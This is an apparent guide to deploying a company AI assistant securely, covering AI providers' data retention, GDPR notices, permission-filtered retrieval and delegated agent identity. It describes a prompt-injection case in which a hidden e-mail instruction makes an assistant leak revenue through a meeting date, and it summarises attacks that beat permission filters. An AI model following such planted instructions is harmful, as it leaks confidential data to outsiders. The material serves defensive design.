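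Providers also change their terms. The Decoder's *Claude users must now opt out* reported that Anthropic gave personal account holders until 28 September 2025 to decide whether it could train on their chats. Simon (2025), in *Azure OpenAI Data Retention Privacy 2025*, noticed that Microsoft had removed a statement that it stored prompts for up to 30 days, and asked on Microsoft's forum whether the limit still applied. Defaults can also depend on when a project was created. For paid Gemini Developer API projects created on or after 26 October 2026, Google logs ordinary calls by default, in addition to its abuse logs. The wholesaler should save a dated copy of the terms it relies on and compare it with the current version every few months.

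### What zero data retention leaves out

Companies usually have to apply for zero data retention, and every provider makes exceptions.

| Developer interface | How to get it | What the provider may still keep | Features that store data anyway | Terms as of |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI API | OpenAI's approval | Images flagged as possible child abuse; flagged content if OpenAI withdraws the arrangement for a model | Files, batches, saved conversations, hosted indexes | November 2026 |
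| Anthropic API | Request to the sales team | Flagged content for up to 2 years; data the law requires it to keep | Files, batches (29 days), code execution (up to 30 days) | December 2026 |
| Google: Gemini Developer API | Google's approval, per project | A log record without user content | Search and Maps grounding (30 days), files, saved conversations | May 2026 |
| Google Cloud | A suitable contract and several settings | Logs for some advanced models | Search grounding (3 days), Maps grounding (30 days), saved conversations | October 2026 |
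| Microsoft Azure | Approval for "modified abuse monitoring" | Nothing for human review, though automated checks continue | Responses API, files, saved threads | October 2025 |

Grounding means letting the model look up facts in Google Search or Maps. When a program uses Search grounding through the Developer API, Google stores the prompt, the context and the answer for 30 days. On Google Cloud, it keeps only the resulting queries and some context for three days, without linking them to the customer. The wholesaler's terms for the same feature could therefore depend on which service it uses.

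Providers often do not offer zero data retention for the chat products that staff use directly. Anthropic, for example, does not offer it for the ordinary chat interfaces of its Team and Enterprise plans. If an administrator turns off conversation history in the Gemini app, Google still saves new chats for up to 72 hours.

The most capable models now have stricter data retention terms. Since 9 June 2026, Anthropic has required data to be kept for 30 days for what it calls Covered Models, even for customers who had zero data retention. Anthropic's *Covered Models* lists Claude Fable 5.2 but not Claude Opus 5.5. Anthropic argues that some attacks are visible only across many requests, such as when someone sends hundreds of variations of a forbidden prompt in the hope that one works. Buying a model through another company doesn't necessarily avoid retention. Google logs prompts and responses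 for up to 30 days when its cloud customers use Claude Fable or OpenAI's recent GPT models, unless the model's developer approves an exemption.

Banks, hospitals and law firms found this hard to accept. In September, Anthropic's *Developing Enterprise Frontier Safeguards with our customers* announced a system that keeps the monitoring data in the customer's own cloud account. Anthropic's software analyses the data and sends any warnings to the customer, and no Anthropic employee needs to read the data. Until the system is ready, some customers can use the Fable models without retention. OpenAI's *Offering Zero Data Retention for frontier models* (2026) had proposed a similar arrangement in August. As The Stack pointed out, Anthropic's system still requires customers to store data that the provider's software can monitor. Customers therefore have another sensitive data store to secure and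 pay for.

The wholesaler's assistant probably doesn't need a Covered Model to decide whether broken glassware qualifies for a refund. The wholesaler should still record its decision not to use one, because a developer who later switches to a Fable model may also need to turn on 30-day retention. Anthropic lets a company turn on retention for a single workspace, so other projects can keep zero data retention.

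A company can check some of these settings. On Azure, the technical description of the resource should show `ContentLogging` with the value `false`. If the entry is missing, Microsoft has not turned off storage for abuse monitoring. OpenAI displays the setting for each project, and for approved customers it treats `store` as false even if the code sets it to true. Anthropic's arrangement is easier to break by accident, because its API generally accepts requests that use features zero data retention doesn't cover. If a developer uploads a file, for example, the upload works and Anthropic stores the file. The wholesaler should therefore review its code for every feature in the table, because a request can succeed without being covered.

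### The preservation order against OpenAI

A court can also override a provider's promise to delete data. The New York Times sued OpenAI and Microsoft for copyright infringement in December 2023. The newspaper and other publishers argued that OpenAI was deleting chats that might show ChatGPT reproducing their articles. On 13 May 2025 Ona Wang, a magistrate judge in New York, ordered OpenAI to preserve output logs it would otherwise have deleted, including those users had asked it to delete.

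According to OpenAI, the order covered ChatGPT Free, Plus, Pro and Team, as well as API customers without zero data retention. It exempted ChatGPT Enterprise, ChatGPT Edu and API customers with zero data retention. Team was a business plan, so a small company paying for business terms could still have had its deleted chats preserved.

OpenAI objected on privacy grounds, and a district judge upheld the order in June. The duty to preserve new chats ended on 26 September 2025, but OpenAI had to keep what it had already saved and continue preserving data from accounts the publishers had flagged. In November the magistrate judge ordered OpenAI to hand over a sample of 20 million consumer conversations with identifying details removed. The district judge upheld that decision in January 2026.

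The 30-day limit failed for several months, and customers could do nothing about it, although the publishers' lawyers were not free to publish the chats and few users are likely to suffer any harm. The wholesaler is best protected if the provider never stores the text, but a court can still order the wholesaler to preserve its own logs.

### The dispute over a CRISPR-like discovery

The court order was public, but customers have a much harder time telling whether a provider has misused data internally, as a dispute in autumn 2026 showed. In September, Anthropic announced that about 950 Claude agents had searched DNA databases for 21 hours and found a new enzyme system resembling CRISPR, the bacterial defence system that biologists adapted for editing genes.

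Mario Rodríguez Mestre, who did doctoral research at the University of Copenhagen, considered Anthropic's CRISPR-like discovery "essentially the same finding" as unpublished work that the Copenhagen team had shared with Claude (CNN, *Anthropic's 'Claude-led' CRISPR-like discovery is sparking controversy*, October 2026). He did not allege deliberate copying, but thought it more likely that people had guided the search more than Anthropic suggested.

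The New York Times reported in *Did Anthropic's AI really make a scientific discovery on its own?* (September 2026) that Anthropic said Claude was not trained on user transcripts and that its biology team could not access them. The overlap does not prove otherwise, since two groups that search similar databases for similar enzymes may well find the same one. But the Copenhagen team had to rely on Anthropic's statement because it could not check the company's training data or access records.

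A customer can prepare for such a dispute by keeping dated records of its work and of what it sent to the provider. It can also ask the provider for an independent audit report or for records of who has opened its data. Anthropic offers these access logs to some organisations that use Covered Models. For unpublished research or a planned takeover, it is safer to withhold the decisive details.

### What the law requires users to be told

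Suppose the wholesaler operates in the EU, since it pays refunds in euros. Under the General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the EU's main privacy law, it is the controller, the party that decides why and how to use personal data. The AI provider is normally the processor, which handles the data on the wholesaler's instructions. The wholesaler therefore has to tell people how their data is used, even though the provider's computers do much of the work. Most of its customers are businesses, but their e-mails come from named individuals, whom the GDPR protects.

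Article 13 applies when a company collects data directly from a person, such as a customer who writes an e-mail or an employee who types a question. At that point the company must explain who it is, why and on what legal basis it uses the data, who receives the data, whether the data leaves the EU, and how long it keeps the data. It must also explain people's rights, including the right to complain to a regulator. If it makes significant decisions about people by automated means alone, it must disclose that and describe the logic involved. A company that already holds customer e-mails and wants to use them for a new purpose must tell people first.

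Article 14 covers personal data that comes from someone other than the person it describes. If a customer writes that she is in hospital and her daughter is handling the account, the wholesaler now holds data about the daughter. It must normally give the daughter similar information, along with the source and type of data, within a month, or at first contact if it writes to her sooner. There are exceptions, such as where informing someone would take disproportionate effort, but the wholesaler should not assume that they cover everybody its customers mention.

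The EU AI Act adds a narrower duty, which has applied since 2 August 2026. Under Article 50, the provider of an AI system that interacts directly with people must design it so that they know by the first interaction that they are dealing with AI, unless this is obvious. The wholesaler can count as the provider, even though another company developed the model, because it builds the assistant and puts it into service under its own name. If an employee reads and sends every reply, the customer is arguably corresponding with a person. The wholesaler can avoid that argument by disclosing the assistant whether or not an employee reviews the replies.

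The drafts below assume that the provider keeps text for 30 days. They are short first notices that link to a full privacy notice, which has to contain the remaining information that the GDPR requires. The staff version could appear above the chat window:

> This assistant is an AI system. It sends your question, with passages from company documents, to our AI provider. The provider keeps this text for up to 30 days to detect misuse, or longer if its software flags the text or the law requires it. It does not train its models on the text. We also log questions and answers, and authorised IT staff can read these logs. Do not enter passwords or medical information. Do not put company or customer data into a personal AI account, even one from the same provider. Check amounts and dates before you act on them. The privacy notice on the intranet explains your rights and whom to contact.

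The customer version belongs next to the e-mail address on the website and in the automatic acknowledgement:

> We use an AI assistant to help answer e-mails about orders. It reads your message and order details, prepares replies and can issue some refunds. One of our employees makes every decision to refuse a refund, and you can ask to deal with a person at any time. An AI provider processes your message for us and keeps it for up to 30 days to detect misuse, or longer if its software flags the message or the law requires it. It does not train its models on your message. Please do not send card numbers or medical details. Our privacy notice explains how to see, correct or delete your data, object to its use, or complain to a regulator.

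These statements must match the actual system. If the wholesaler obtains zero data retention, it can remove the mention of 30 days but should keep the exceptions. In some EU countries it may also have to consult employee representatives before it logs what staff type.

### Staff who use personal accounts

The wholesaler's contracts with AI providers do not apply when an employee pastes a supplier contract into a personal account. The provider may train on the text, and a reviewer may read it. Google warns users of the personal Gemini app not to enter confidential information they would not want a reviewer to see. The wholesaler cannot delete the chat or search it when a customer asks for their data, and the employee keeps the account after leaving.

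The Gemini app looks much the same with a personal account as with a work account, but the terms differ, and many employees probably don't realise when the work terms no longer apply. Turning off the training setting helps only partly. With the activity setting off, Google still keeps chats from personal accounts for 72 hours and may use human reviewers to protect its services and users.

The wholesaler should give staff an approved assistant that does the jobs for which they now use their own accounts. The company can then block personal accounts on its computers and use DLP rules to catch uploads of sensitive files. Blocking alone is likely to lead some people to use their phones instead, where the company can't see what they share. If someone reports having pasted a contract into a personal account, the company should help them delete the chat promptly and record what the provider may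 still hold. Punishing the first person who reports this would discourage others from coming forward.

### Hosting the model elsewhere

A company can avoid the model provider's terms by running an open-weight model, whose trained parameters anyone can download, on its own computers. Prompts then stay inside the company, so nobody else can train on them or change how long they are kept.

A company that runs the model itself takes on the provider's work. It needs expensive processors and people to run them, and it has to install security updates and replace the model when a better one appears. If the wholesaler's 3,000 staff each ask ten questions a day, the hardware has to answer about one question per second over an eight-hour day. It also has to handle a Monday morning peak several times higher, though it is mostly idle overnight. The company loses the provider's abuse monitoring and has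 to test for itself how well the model resists prompt injection. Its own server logs may still contain every prompt, so it has to set and enforce a retention period for them.

Using a model through a large cloud company is a middle option. Microsoft runs OpenAI's models on Azure without giving OpenAI the prompts. It also acts as the data processor for other models in its catalogue that it hosts as a service. This suits companies that already trust Microsoft with their documents and mail, but they still have to check the terms for each model. Google, for instance, says customers who use Claude Fable 5 on its cloud must allow it to share prompts and responses with Anthropic for abuse monitoring, whereas Anthropic says the retained data stays in Google's environment. A customer who needs certainty should have its contract state who receives its data.

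For the wholesaler, a hosted model with zero data retention and a search index on its own computers is probably the best balance. Self-hosting would make more sense if the wholesaler handled medical records or defence contracts, or if its customers' contracts prohibited sending data to any outside AI provider.

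## Showing each user only the documents they may read

A search index on the wholesaler's own computers keeps most of the text away from the provider, but it puts passages from many confidential files in one place. The software that builds the index needs permission to read all those files. Unless the application checks each employee's permissions on every search, a warehouse employee can receive a passage from a contract that only the purchasing team may open.

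### From access list to context window

A document store keeps an access list of the people and groups that may open each file. The indexing software cuts the file into passages and stores the file's identifier, version and access list with each one. Groups are easier to maintain than individual names because adding a new buyer to the purchasing group avoids updating the access lists on thousands of passages. The software has to copy the permissions that actually apply, including those inherited from the file's folder and any entry that denies access. If it cannot read a file's access list, it should leave the file out of the index.

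When an employee asks a question, the application takes the employee's identity from the access token and looks up their groups. It must never take the identity from the conversation, since anyone can type "I am the finance director". (The next section covers delegated tokens, which carry the identity on to other systems.) The application then sends the groups and the question to the database together. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, with an extension for searching by meaning, a simplified query might be:

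```sql
SELECT file_id, passage
FROM passages
WHERE allowed_groups && :groups_of_employee
ORDER BY embedding <=> :question
LIMIT 10;
```

An embedding is a list of numbers that represents a passage's meaning. The third line keeps only passages whose access list includes at least one of the employee's groups, the fourth sorts them by closeness to the question, and the last takes the ten closest.

A programmer can forget the third line or get it wrong. *Beyond Similarity Search* (2026) compared two systems that each held data for several customers. In one, a bug in the application code leaked another customer's data in two of 1,000 queries. The other filtered in the database engine and leaked nothing. Two leaks are too few to estimate a rate, but filtering in the database does protect against a forgotten condition. With PostgreSQL's row-level security, for example, the database adds the permission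 condition to every query, even if the programmer omits it.

Before any passage goes to the model, the application checks with the document store that the employee can open the file now. *Towards Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2026), a review of defences, also describes repeating the permission check at this point. Ten passages need at most ten quick lookups. If the store does not respond, the application should drop the passage. The second check catches access rights revoked since the last copy. It does not add documents the employee has just gained permission to read, but this omission is only an inconvenience.

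The application can now build the context window. It drops passages with sensitivity labels that company policy excludes, and a retrieval rail can inspect the rest. It should also log what happened. *AGL-1* (2026), a proposed design for governing company AI systems, lists what the log should contain at minimum: the query, the identity of the user or agent, the permission decision and the reason for it, and the identifiers and versions of the sources. The wholesaler can then check later why an employee saw a particular clause.

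### Filtering before or after the search

The query above filters first and then ranks. Many systems instead find the ten closest passages in the whole index and then remove those the employee may not read. Suppose an employee may read 20% of the documents, and permission is unrelated to relevance. On average, two of the ten passages remain. For about 11% of questions (0.8¹⁰), none remain, even though the index holds thousands of passages that the employee may read.

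The usual remedy is to fetch more candidates before filtering:

| Candidates fetched | Readable on average | Chance that none is readable | Chance that fewer than ten are readable |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 2 | 11% | Almost 100% |
| 50 | 10 | 0.001% | 44% |
| 100 | 20 | Practically zero | 0.2% |

*Don't Stir the Pot! Authorized Vector Data Retrieval via Access-Aware Indexing* (Han, Chakraborty and Mehrotra, 2026) calls the fivefold increase in the second row the "inflation factor". It is the number of passages in the index divided by the number the user may read, rounded up. The search has to examine proportionally more candidates. In the table, fetching five times as many gives ten readable results on average, but 44% of searches still return fewer than ten.

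Assuming that permissions are independent of relevance is optimistic, because permissions tend to follow subjects. When a warehouse employee asks about breakages, the 100 closest passages may all come from supplier contracts the employee cannot read, while the handling guide that would help ranks 130th. Filtering by permission before selecting the closest passages finds the guide.

Filtering after ranking can work just as well as filtering before it if there are always enough candidates. *Audience-Bound Persistent Memory* (2026) tested an assistant that stores memories belonging to different people. Without permission checks, 82% of 100,000 context windows contained something forbidden. None did when the filter ran either before or after ranking, and both orders found the permitted evidence equally often. However, the late filter examined 20 candidates and each test contained only eight distracting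 items, so it could never run out of candidates.

*Protection Is Not One Event* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 118 studies, concludes that late checks are far riskier than early ones. It cites an experiment by Namboothiri in which retrieving first and filtering afterwards exposed unauthorised text in 86.1% of queries. That is close to the 82% for no filtering, so it probably counts passages that the search returned before the filter removed them. Such passages need not reach the model, but they have already passed through the application, and perhaps its logs, where a bug could expose them.

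Filtering first can be slow, because the database may have to compare the question with every permitted passage. If the wholesaler's documents produce 400,000 passages and an employee may read 80,000, a modern server can make those 80,000 comparisons in well under a second. Larger collections need approximate indexes, which examine only part of the data. Some databases run the approximate search first and then apply the permission condition to the results, even though the query looks like the one above. An engineer can test for this by logging in as someone with very few permissions and counting the results.

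### What a hidden document gives away

Suppose the wholesaler's search page counts matching documents before it removes the forbidden ones. An employee at the Lyon depot types "Lyon depot closure" and sees "4 documents found, 0 shown". The same search for two other depots finds nothing. Without reading any of the documents, the employee can guess which depot the company is thinking of closing. Adding "March" or "April" to the search and watching the number change may also reveal the month.

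Filtering after the search can reveal how many hidden passages matched, even if the page doesn't display a count. If the application always fetches ten passages and shows two, the employee can work out that eight of the ten closest were hidden. In keyword search, relevance scores can also depend on how many documents in the index contain a word, including hidden ones. *Plaintext Recovery Against Post-Filtering Access Control* (2026) concerns a worse outcome, in which an attacker recovers hidden text despite the filter.

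Clarifying questions can leak names. If an employee asks about "the Weiss agreement", the assistant might ask whether they mean the delivery agreement or the takeover agreement. *Beyond Document Retrieval* (2026) therefore recommends applying permissions outside the model and before the user sees any candidates.

The application should calculate counts, suggestions and scores only from permitted documents, and give the same reply whether a document doesn't exist or the employee may not read it. But an employee with a legitimate need for a document then won't know there is one to request. Copilot instead shows users a notice that it left out relevant content because of company policy. That notice is probably harmless if the content is a supplier contract, but it would be a serious leak if the content concerned a depot closure.

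### Permissions that change

The index holds a copy of the access list, and the original keeps changing. If the software copies permissions once a day and revocations happen at random times, a revoked right keeps working in the index for twelve hours on average and almost twenty-four at worst. With ten revocations a day, about five revoked rights still work at any moment. Copying every 15 minutes cuts the average delay to seven and a half minutes. Some document stores can also send a notification when permissions change, but notifications can get lost, so the wholesaler still needs to copy all permissions regularly.

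The check at the source closes most of this gap for searches, but it does not cover material the application has already derived from a document and can use without searching again.

| What survives | How it can expose data | Remedy |
|---|---|---|
| Passage in the index | Its access list is out of date | Update the list on every change and check at the source |
| Embedding | The database may only mark it as deleted | Rebuild the index, or encrypt the embedding and destroy the key |
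| Summary | It combines documents with different readers | Record the sources and require permission for all of them |
| Cached answer | The application returns it without a search | Reuse it only after checking the new user's permission for every source |
| Conversation memory | An old note enters a new context window | Store each note's sources and check them before every use |

Cached answers are easy to overlook. If a purchasing manager asks about a supplier's discount and the application caches the answer to save money, a warehouse employee who later asks the same question may receive it because the document filter never runs. The same can happen with the assistant's memory when someone changes jobs. After a buyer moves to sales, the assistant may still use an old note about the discount. The former buyer may remember the figure, but the assistant should not keep supplying details the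 person has forgotten.

Deleted embeddings are a smaller risk, because an attacker needs access to the index itself. A common type of index links each embedding to its neighbours. Removing an entry can break these links, so databases often just mark it as deleted. *Ghost Vectors* (2026) found that attackers could still reconstruct text from such entries. Liu and colleagues report that the reconstructions scored 0.207 on a measure of word overlap that runs from 0 to 1, and that encrypting the entries and discarding the key reduced the score to zero. On clinical notes, reconstructions from unprotected entries scored only 0.009, because the software handled medical language poorly. The wholesaler should still rebuild its index periodically, since attack software will improve.

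### Roles, attributes and separate indexes

Most companies start with role-based rules, such as "purchasing staff may read supplier contracts". These rules are easy to explain and audit, but exceptions multiply. If access depends on six departments, five countries and three levels of seniority, a wholesaler could need 90 roles.

An attribute-based rule combines facts about the person, the document and the situation. For example, a rule might let buyers read contracts for their own country until the contract ends. A right with an end date expires without anyone having to revoke it. *AGL-1* lists other possible attributes, including data classification, the customer relationship and the purpose of the request. These rules depend on every attribute being correct. Liu and colleagues cite a study in which defences remained vulnerable when 5% to 10% of document labels were wrong. They also cite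 a confidentiality filter that caught only 74.35% of cases when questions did not name the project. The wholesaler could use roles for most documents and add attributes such as country and end date where roles are too coarse. Purpose is harder to use because the application usually has to infer it from what the employee types.

The wholesaler also has to decide whether to keep everything in one index. A separate index for each role contains only passages that role may read, so the search needs no filter and hidden documents cannot affect the number of results. But a passage that five roles may read has to be stored and updated five times. In an example by Han and colleagues with 10,000 entries and three roles, separate indexes take 1.5 times the storage of a shared one. Their own method, which copies only the most useful groups of entries, takes 1.2 times. They find that separate indexes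 suit users who may read little of the collection, while a shared index with filtering after the search is more efficient for those who may read most of it.

Researchers have also tried to build permissions into the embeddings, for example by rotating them differently for each policy so that only a matching query finds them. *Isolation Is Not Confidentiality* (2026) examines the security of these schemes and, as its title suggests, separating documents this way may not keep them confidential. With only 40,000 documents, the wholesaler can use one shared index that filters by permission before searching, plus a separate one for the few projects, such as a takeover, where a filtering mistake would be especially harmful.

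### When someone else reads the answer

Checking the employee's permissions is not enough when the assistant writes to a customer. *Enterprise AI Must Enforce Participant-Aware Access Control* (Bhatt, Rajore and colleagues, 2025) describes an attack in which Bob e-mails Alice to suggest a meeting. The e-mail contains a hidden instruction for her assistant to look up a project's revenue and propose the day of the month that matches the figure in millions. Alice may read the figure, so the filter lets her assistant use it. The assistant drafts "how about 7th May?", Alice approves it, and Bob learns that the revenue is $7 million.

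Neither Alice's review nor a DLP scan is likely to catch an ordinary date. Bhatt and colleagues at Microsoft propose that the context window should contain only documents that all participants may read, including everyone copied into the e-mail. If the assistant needs any other document, it must ask Alice for explicit consent, or leave the document out if it sends messages without review.

This strict rule would make the wholesaler's assistant less useful, because refund decisions can depend on supplier contracts that customers may not see. The application can split the work into two steps. The first step reads the internal documents and produces only a decision and an amount, which ordinary code checks. The second step writes the reply from that decision, the published returns policy and the customer's own order. It does not receive the contract text, so a customer's hidden instruction cannot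 make it reveal that text in the reply.

### Asking the model to enforce permissions

A filter controls which documents the model receives, but not what it does with them. Sun, Zhang and colleagues (2026) argue in *PERMIT* that the model can still infer or recombine information in ways that a document filter misses. Suppose an employee may read a budget that gives €540,000 for team leaders' pay and a rota that names twelve team leaders. Each document seems harmless, but the assistant can combine them to work out that the average team leader earns €45,000.

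Output filters have a similar problem. Liu and colleagues tested one that removed any run of eight tokens matching a protected document. It stopped all long word-for-word copying, but an attacker who asked three questions, adapting each to the previous reply, still recovered 48.3% of the hidden facts from one small model. Researchers have therefore tried to make the model itself respect permissions.

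The simplest method is to give the model the access rules as text. *Role-Conditioned Refusals* (Klisura, Khoury and colleagues, 2025) added permissions for four roles to Spider and BIRD, two collections of database questions. The model had to write an SQL query if the role could see the necessary tables and columns, and refuse otherwise. The study tested GPT-4o-mini and versions of DeepSeek-R1, Llama 3.1 and Mistral with 7 to 14 billion parameters. The best F1 scores on Spider, where 1 means no wrong answers and no wrong refusals, were 0.83 for a single model given the policy, 0.88 when a second model checked the first one's query, and 0.93 for a model fine-tuned (trained further) on examples. The fine-tuned model scored only 0.66 on BIRD, which was not in its training data.

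Longer policies led to more errors. The two-model design wrongly permitted 5.5% of queries when policies were about 2,700 characters long and 33% when they were about 22,700. The fine-tuned model wrongly permitted 40% with the longer policies. The paper's other figures suggest that the 33% is a share of all queries, so the share of forbidden queries that got through would be even higher. Some smaller models also wrote "Access Denied" and then produced the forbidden query.

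Li, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Chain-of-Authorization*, fine-tuned three small models to write out, before every answer, which permissions the material requires, which the user has, and whether they match. The models refused nearly 100% of unauthorised requests across five datasets. The researchers counted any response containing "Sorry" as a refusal, so a leak that followed an apology would have counted too, but the models' accuracy on forbidden questions also fell to nearly zero. The two larger models resisted rewritten and persuasive prompts almost completely. The smallest, with 1.7 billion parameters, failed on up to 9.12% of attacks when the user had no permissions. The method can reduce accuracy on permitted questions. Mistral scored 57% on a general-knowledge test, against 67% after ordinary fine-tuning.

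Two other studies change the numbers that a model computes internally while it processes text. Zhang, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *Activation-Space Anchored Access Control for Multi-Class Permission Reasoning in Large Language Models*, calculate a typical pattern of these numbers for each of five departments. If a request's pattern is close to the one for the user's department, the model answers normally. If it is far away, the system refuses. In between, the system pushes the numbers towards the permitted pattern. The method requires no training. Restricted terms appeared at a rate of 0.5% to 0.9%, but the questions were not a hard test, because the rate was only 2.5% to 4.7% even for models without any rules. Attacks in which users pretended to have another role succeeded 8.4% to 10.1% of the time.

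Permit, Sun and colleagues' method, learns which of a model's internal numbers vary with permissions and trains a small correction for each permission level. The test gave the model a full medical record and asked for details that the user was only partly allowed to see. Without any rules, the models leaked restricted details roughly 97% of the time. Writing the rules into the prompt reduced this to 9.0% for Llama and 42.2% for Qwen. The better version of Permit reduced it to 0.0% for Llama and 2.5% for Qwen.

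| Study | Models | Errors in ordinary tests | Errors under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Klisura and colleagues, October 2025 | GPT-4o-mini and three open models | 5.5% to 40%, depending on design and policy length | Not tested |
| Zhang and colleagues, January 2026 | Llama 3, Qwen3, Gemma | 0.5% to 0.9% | 8.4% to 10.1% |
| Li and colleagues, March 2026 | Qwen3, Llama 3.1, Mistral | 0% to 6.54% | 0% to 9.12% |
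| Sun and colleagues, May 2026 | Llama 3.1, Qwen2.5 | 0.0% to 2.5% | 1.0%, Llama only |

The rates measure different things, so they cannot be used to rank the methods, but they are all too high to protect salaries or contracts. Suppose the wholesaler's staff ask 30,000 questions a day and 1% of them concern information the person asking may not see. A 2.5% error rate would then mean seven or eight disclosures a day. An employee who makes ten independent attempts, each with a 10% chance of success, has a 65% chance of succeeding at least once. Most of these methods also rely on the model to withhold information it already has.

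The argument about inference is sound, but the experiments do not show that these methods solve the problem. Permit's test counted a leak only when the answer literally matched a restricted field, so it would miss a fact that the model had paraphrased or worked out. Zhang and colleagues acknowledge that their method may perform poorly when an answer combines information from several departments. For now, the wholesaler can handle the pay example more reliably by restricting access to the budget. Sun and colleagues recommend Permit as an addition to existing access control.

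Most of the models in these studies are small, and current ones do better. *DEPUTYBENCH* (2026) tested recent frontier models on tasks where even reading a record required permission. Given a checklist of what to verify, every model succeeded on at least 97.2% of these tasks. Without the checklist, the models tended to notice that a record was restricted only after reading it. A filter in ordinary code avoids this problem by keeping restricted records from reaching the model.

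A language model can also act as the filter, judging each passage before the main model receives it. *ARBITER* (2025) describes such a system, built with NeMo Guardrails, that reached 85% accuracy and an F1 score of 0.89. Liu and colleagues point out that a simple fixed filter scored 0.93 to 0.94 on the same task.

### Fine-tuned models have no access list

When a company fine-tunes a model on its documents instead of retrieving them, every document affects many of the model's parameters. Nobody can then attach an access list to what the model learned from a salary spreadsheet, for example. The model may also paraphrase what it learned, and a data loss prevention (DLP) scan cannot tell which document an answer came from.

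Differential privacy is a training method that adds noise to limit the influence of any single record. Bhatt and colleagues explain that it still permits some leakage, and that a company secret usually appears in many related documents. Protecting all of them together requires so much noise that the model becomes much less useful.

One proposal is to let a person use a fine-tuned model only if they may read every document in its training data. The wholesaler should therefore treat anything it uses for fine-tuning as readable by everyone who can query the model. If all 3,000 staff will use the model, the training data must contain only documents that all of them may read. If only the customer service team will use it, the wholesaler can include any document that every member of that team may read.

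Adding documents tends to reduce the number of people who may use the model. Finding the combination that covers the most pairs of people and documents is computationally hard, so Bhatt and colleagues use a shortcut. Their software takes each distinct access list as a possible group of users, collects every document the whole group may read, and adds anyone else who may read all of them. Microsoft uses an initial version of this method in Copilot Tuning, its service for fine-tuning models on a company's data.

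Permissions also change after training. If an employee loses access to a training document, the wholesaler has to withdraw the model from that person or retrain it without the document. With retrieval, it only has to update an access list. The wholesaler would do better to fine-tune the model for the tone and format of its replies, using examples that everyone may read, and supply prices, contracts and customer details through retrieval.

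## Giving the model its own identity and permissions

The filter on the document index needs only the identity of the employee asking. For a refund, the payment system also has to identify whether the request comes from the employee or the assistant. The wholesaler therefore has to decide whether to make the assistant a principal with its own account or have it use somebody else's.

### OWASP's advice

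OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes free guidance on application security, advises developers to "treat the model as any other user, adopting a zero-trust approach". The advice comes from *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, an entry in its 2025 list of the ten main risks for language model applications. The entry is about a fairly narrow problem, and in the same sentence OWASP also tells developers to validate whatever the model sends to other software. If the model requests a refund of minus €40, for example, the refund function should reject the request, just as it would if a visitor had typed it into a web form.

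Under zero trust, each system checks every request, even one from the company's own servers. Many older company networks checked people and programs at the edge and then trusted everything inside. With zero trust, the assistant needs its own account, has to prove its identity when it connects to another system, such as the refund system, and gets only the permissions its work requires.

The current edition of the list, which OWASP (2026) published on 3 August, gives more weight to permissions. Excessive agency, which means giving a model more functions, permissions or independence than it needs, rose from sixth place to third, while output handling fell from fifth to tenth. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), three-quarters of the ranking's weight comes from a vote by practitioners and the rest from a collection of 7,714 real incidents, 6,639 of which had enough detail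 to classify. The vote and the incident data matched most clearly on the rise of excessive agency.

Respan's *OWASP LLM Top 10* (2026) describes a typical case in which a tool that only needs to read a database connects through an account that can also change and delete records. OWASP recommends keeping credentials in trusted code and having ordinary software recheck each privileged request when it runs.

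The account belongs to the assistant, not the model, which many other companies also use. The principal is the wholesaler's application, including its instructions, tools and current model. If the wholesaler switches to a newer model, the account can stay the same, but the log should record the model version because the two models may behave differently.

The application should also keep the assistant's credentials out of the context window. SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications* reports that OWASP tells developers to assume outsiders can discover a model's hidden instructions, and so not to store passwords or tokens in them.

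### Four ways to give the assistant access

Suppose the finance department finds thirty unusual refunds at the end of the month, all linked to Marta, a customer service employee. What the department can learn about them depends on how the AI assistant accesses the refund system.

The quickest way to give the assistant access is for Marta to share her password. The refund log then records every refund under her name, so nobody can tell from it which ones she issued and which the assistant issued. The assistant can also do everything else Marta can, such as open her payslips, and she can cut it off only by changing her password. *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 blog post from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), describes this kind of sharing as already common.

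An agent that runs on an employee's laptop under the employee's own account creates the same problem, even if nobody shares a password. NIST suggests running such agents in a sandbox, a closed-off environment that limits which files and programs they can reach.

An assistant can also ask for a password during a conversation. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common way of connecting models to tools, lets an agent ask the user for more information partway through a task. Its specification warns developers not to use this feature to request sensitive information, but a planted instruction could still lead the assistant to ask for a password. The wholesaler should tell staff that the assistant never needs their password.

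Another arrangement is for the assistant and other programs to share a service account, which is an account for software. The account needs enough permissions for every request that any user might make. If a finance manager may refund €5,000 through the assistant, the account must be able to do so too. A warehouse employee could then persuade the assistant to issue a refund that the employee has no permission to make. This is known as the confused deputy problem.

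Programs often log in to such an account with an API key, a long string of characters that works for anyone who has it and may never expire. NIST notes that companies often leave these keys unprotected in configuration files and logs. Replacing a key interrupts every program that uses it, so engineers have good reason to delay it.

With a separate agent identity, the assistant has an account that no person or other program uses. The finance department can tell the assistant's refunds from Marta's, and an administrator can disable the assistant without affecting anyone else. But the refund system still can't identify who asked for each refund, and it allows the same amount whoever asked.

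Delegated access solves this problem by letting software act for a named user, within limits, under its own identity. The log records its actions under "refund-assistant for marta.k".

| Arrangement | Whom the log names | What the assistant can reach | How to cut it off |
|---|---|---|---|
| User's password | Only the employee | Everything the employee can | Change the employee's password |
| Shared service account | Only the account | Whatever any of its users or programs needs | Replace the key in every program |
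| Separate agent identity | Only the assistant | Whatever the assistant's account allows, whoever asks | Disable the assistant |
| Delegated access | The employee and the assistant | Only what both may do | Disable the assistant, the employee, or the assistant's right to act for that employee |

The wholesaler should use delegated access whenever an employee makes the request. Delegated access requires the assistant to have its own identity, and the assistant can use that identity alone for jobs that no employee requested, such as sorting the customer mailbox overnight.

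### The lowest of three limits

Under delegated access, the assistant's effective permission is the intersection of what the user, the agent and the task allow:

> effective permission = user's permissions ∩ agent's permissions ∩ task's permissions

An action is allowed only if it is in all three sets. When the permission is an amount of money, the lowest of the three limits applies. Suppose a customer reports four broken glasses, at €10 each, in an order worth €240. Marta may refund up to €500, the wholesaler has limited the assistant to €100, and this task justifies €40. The assistant can therefore refund €40.

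| Case | User | Agent | Task | Assistant's limit |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Marta asks about four broken glasses | €500 | €100 | €40 | €40 |
| Marta asks about an order that is entirely broken | €500 | €100 | €240 | €100 |
| A warehouse employee asks about the four glasses | €0 | €100 | €40 | €0 |

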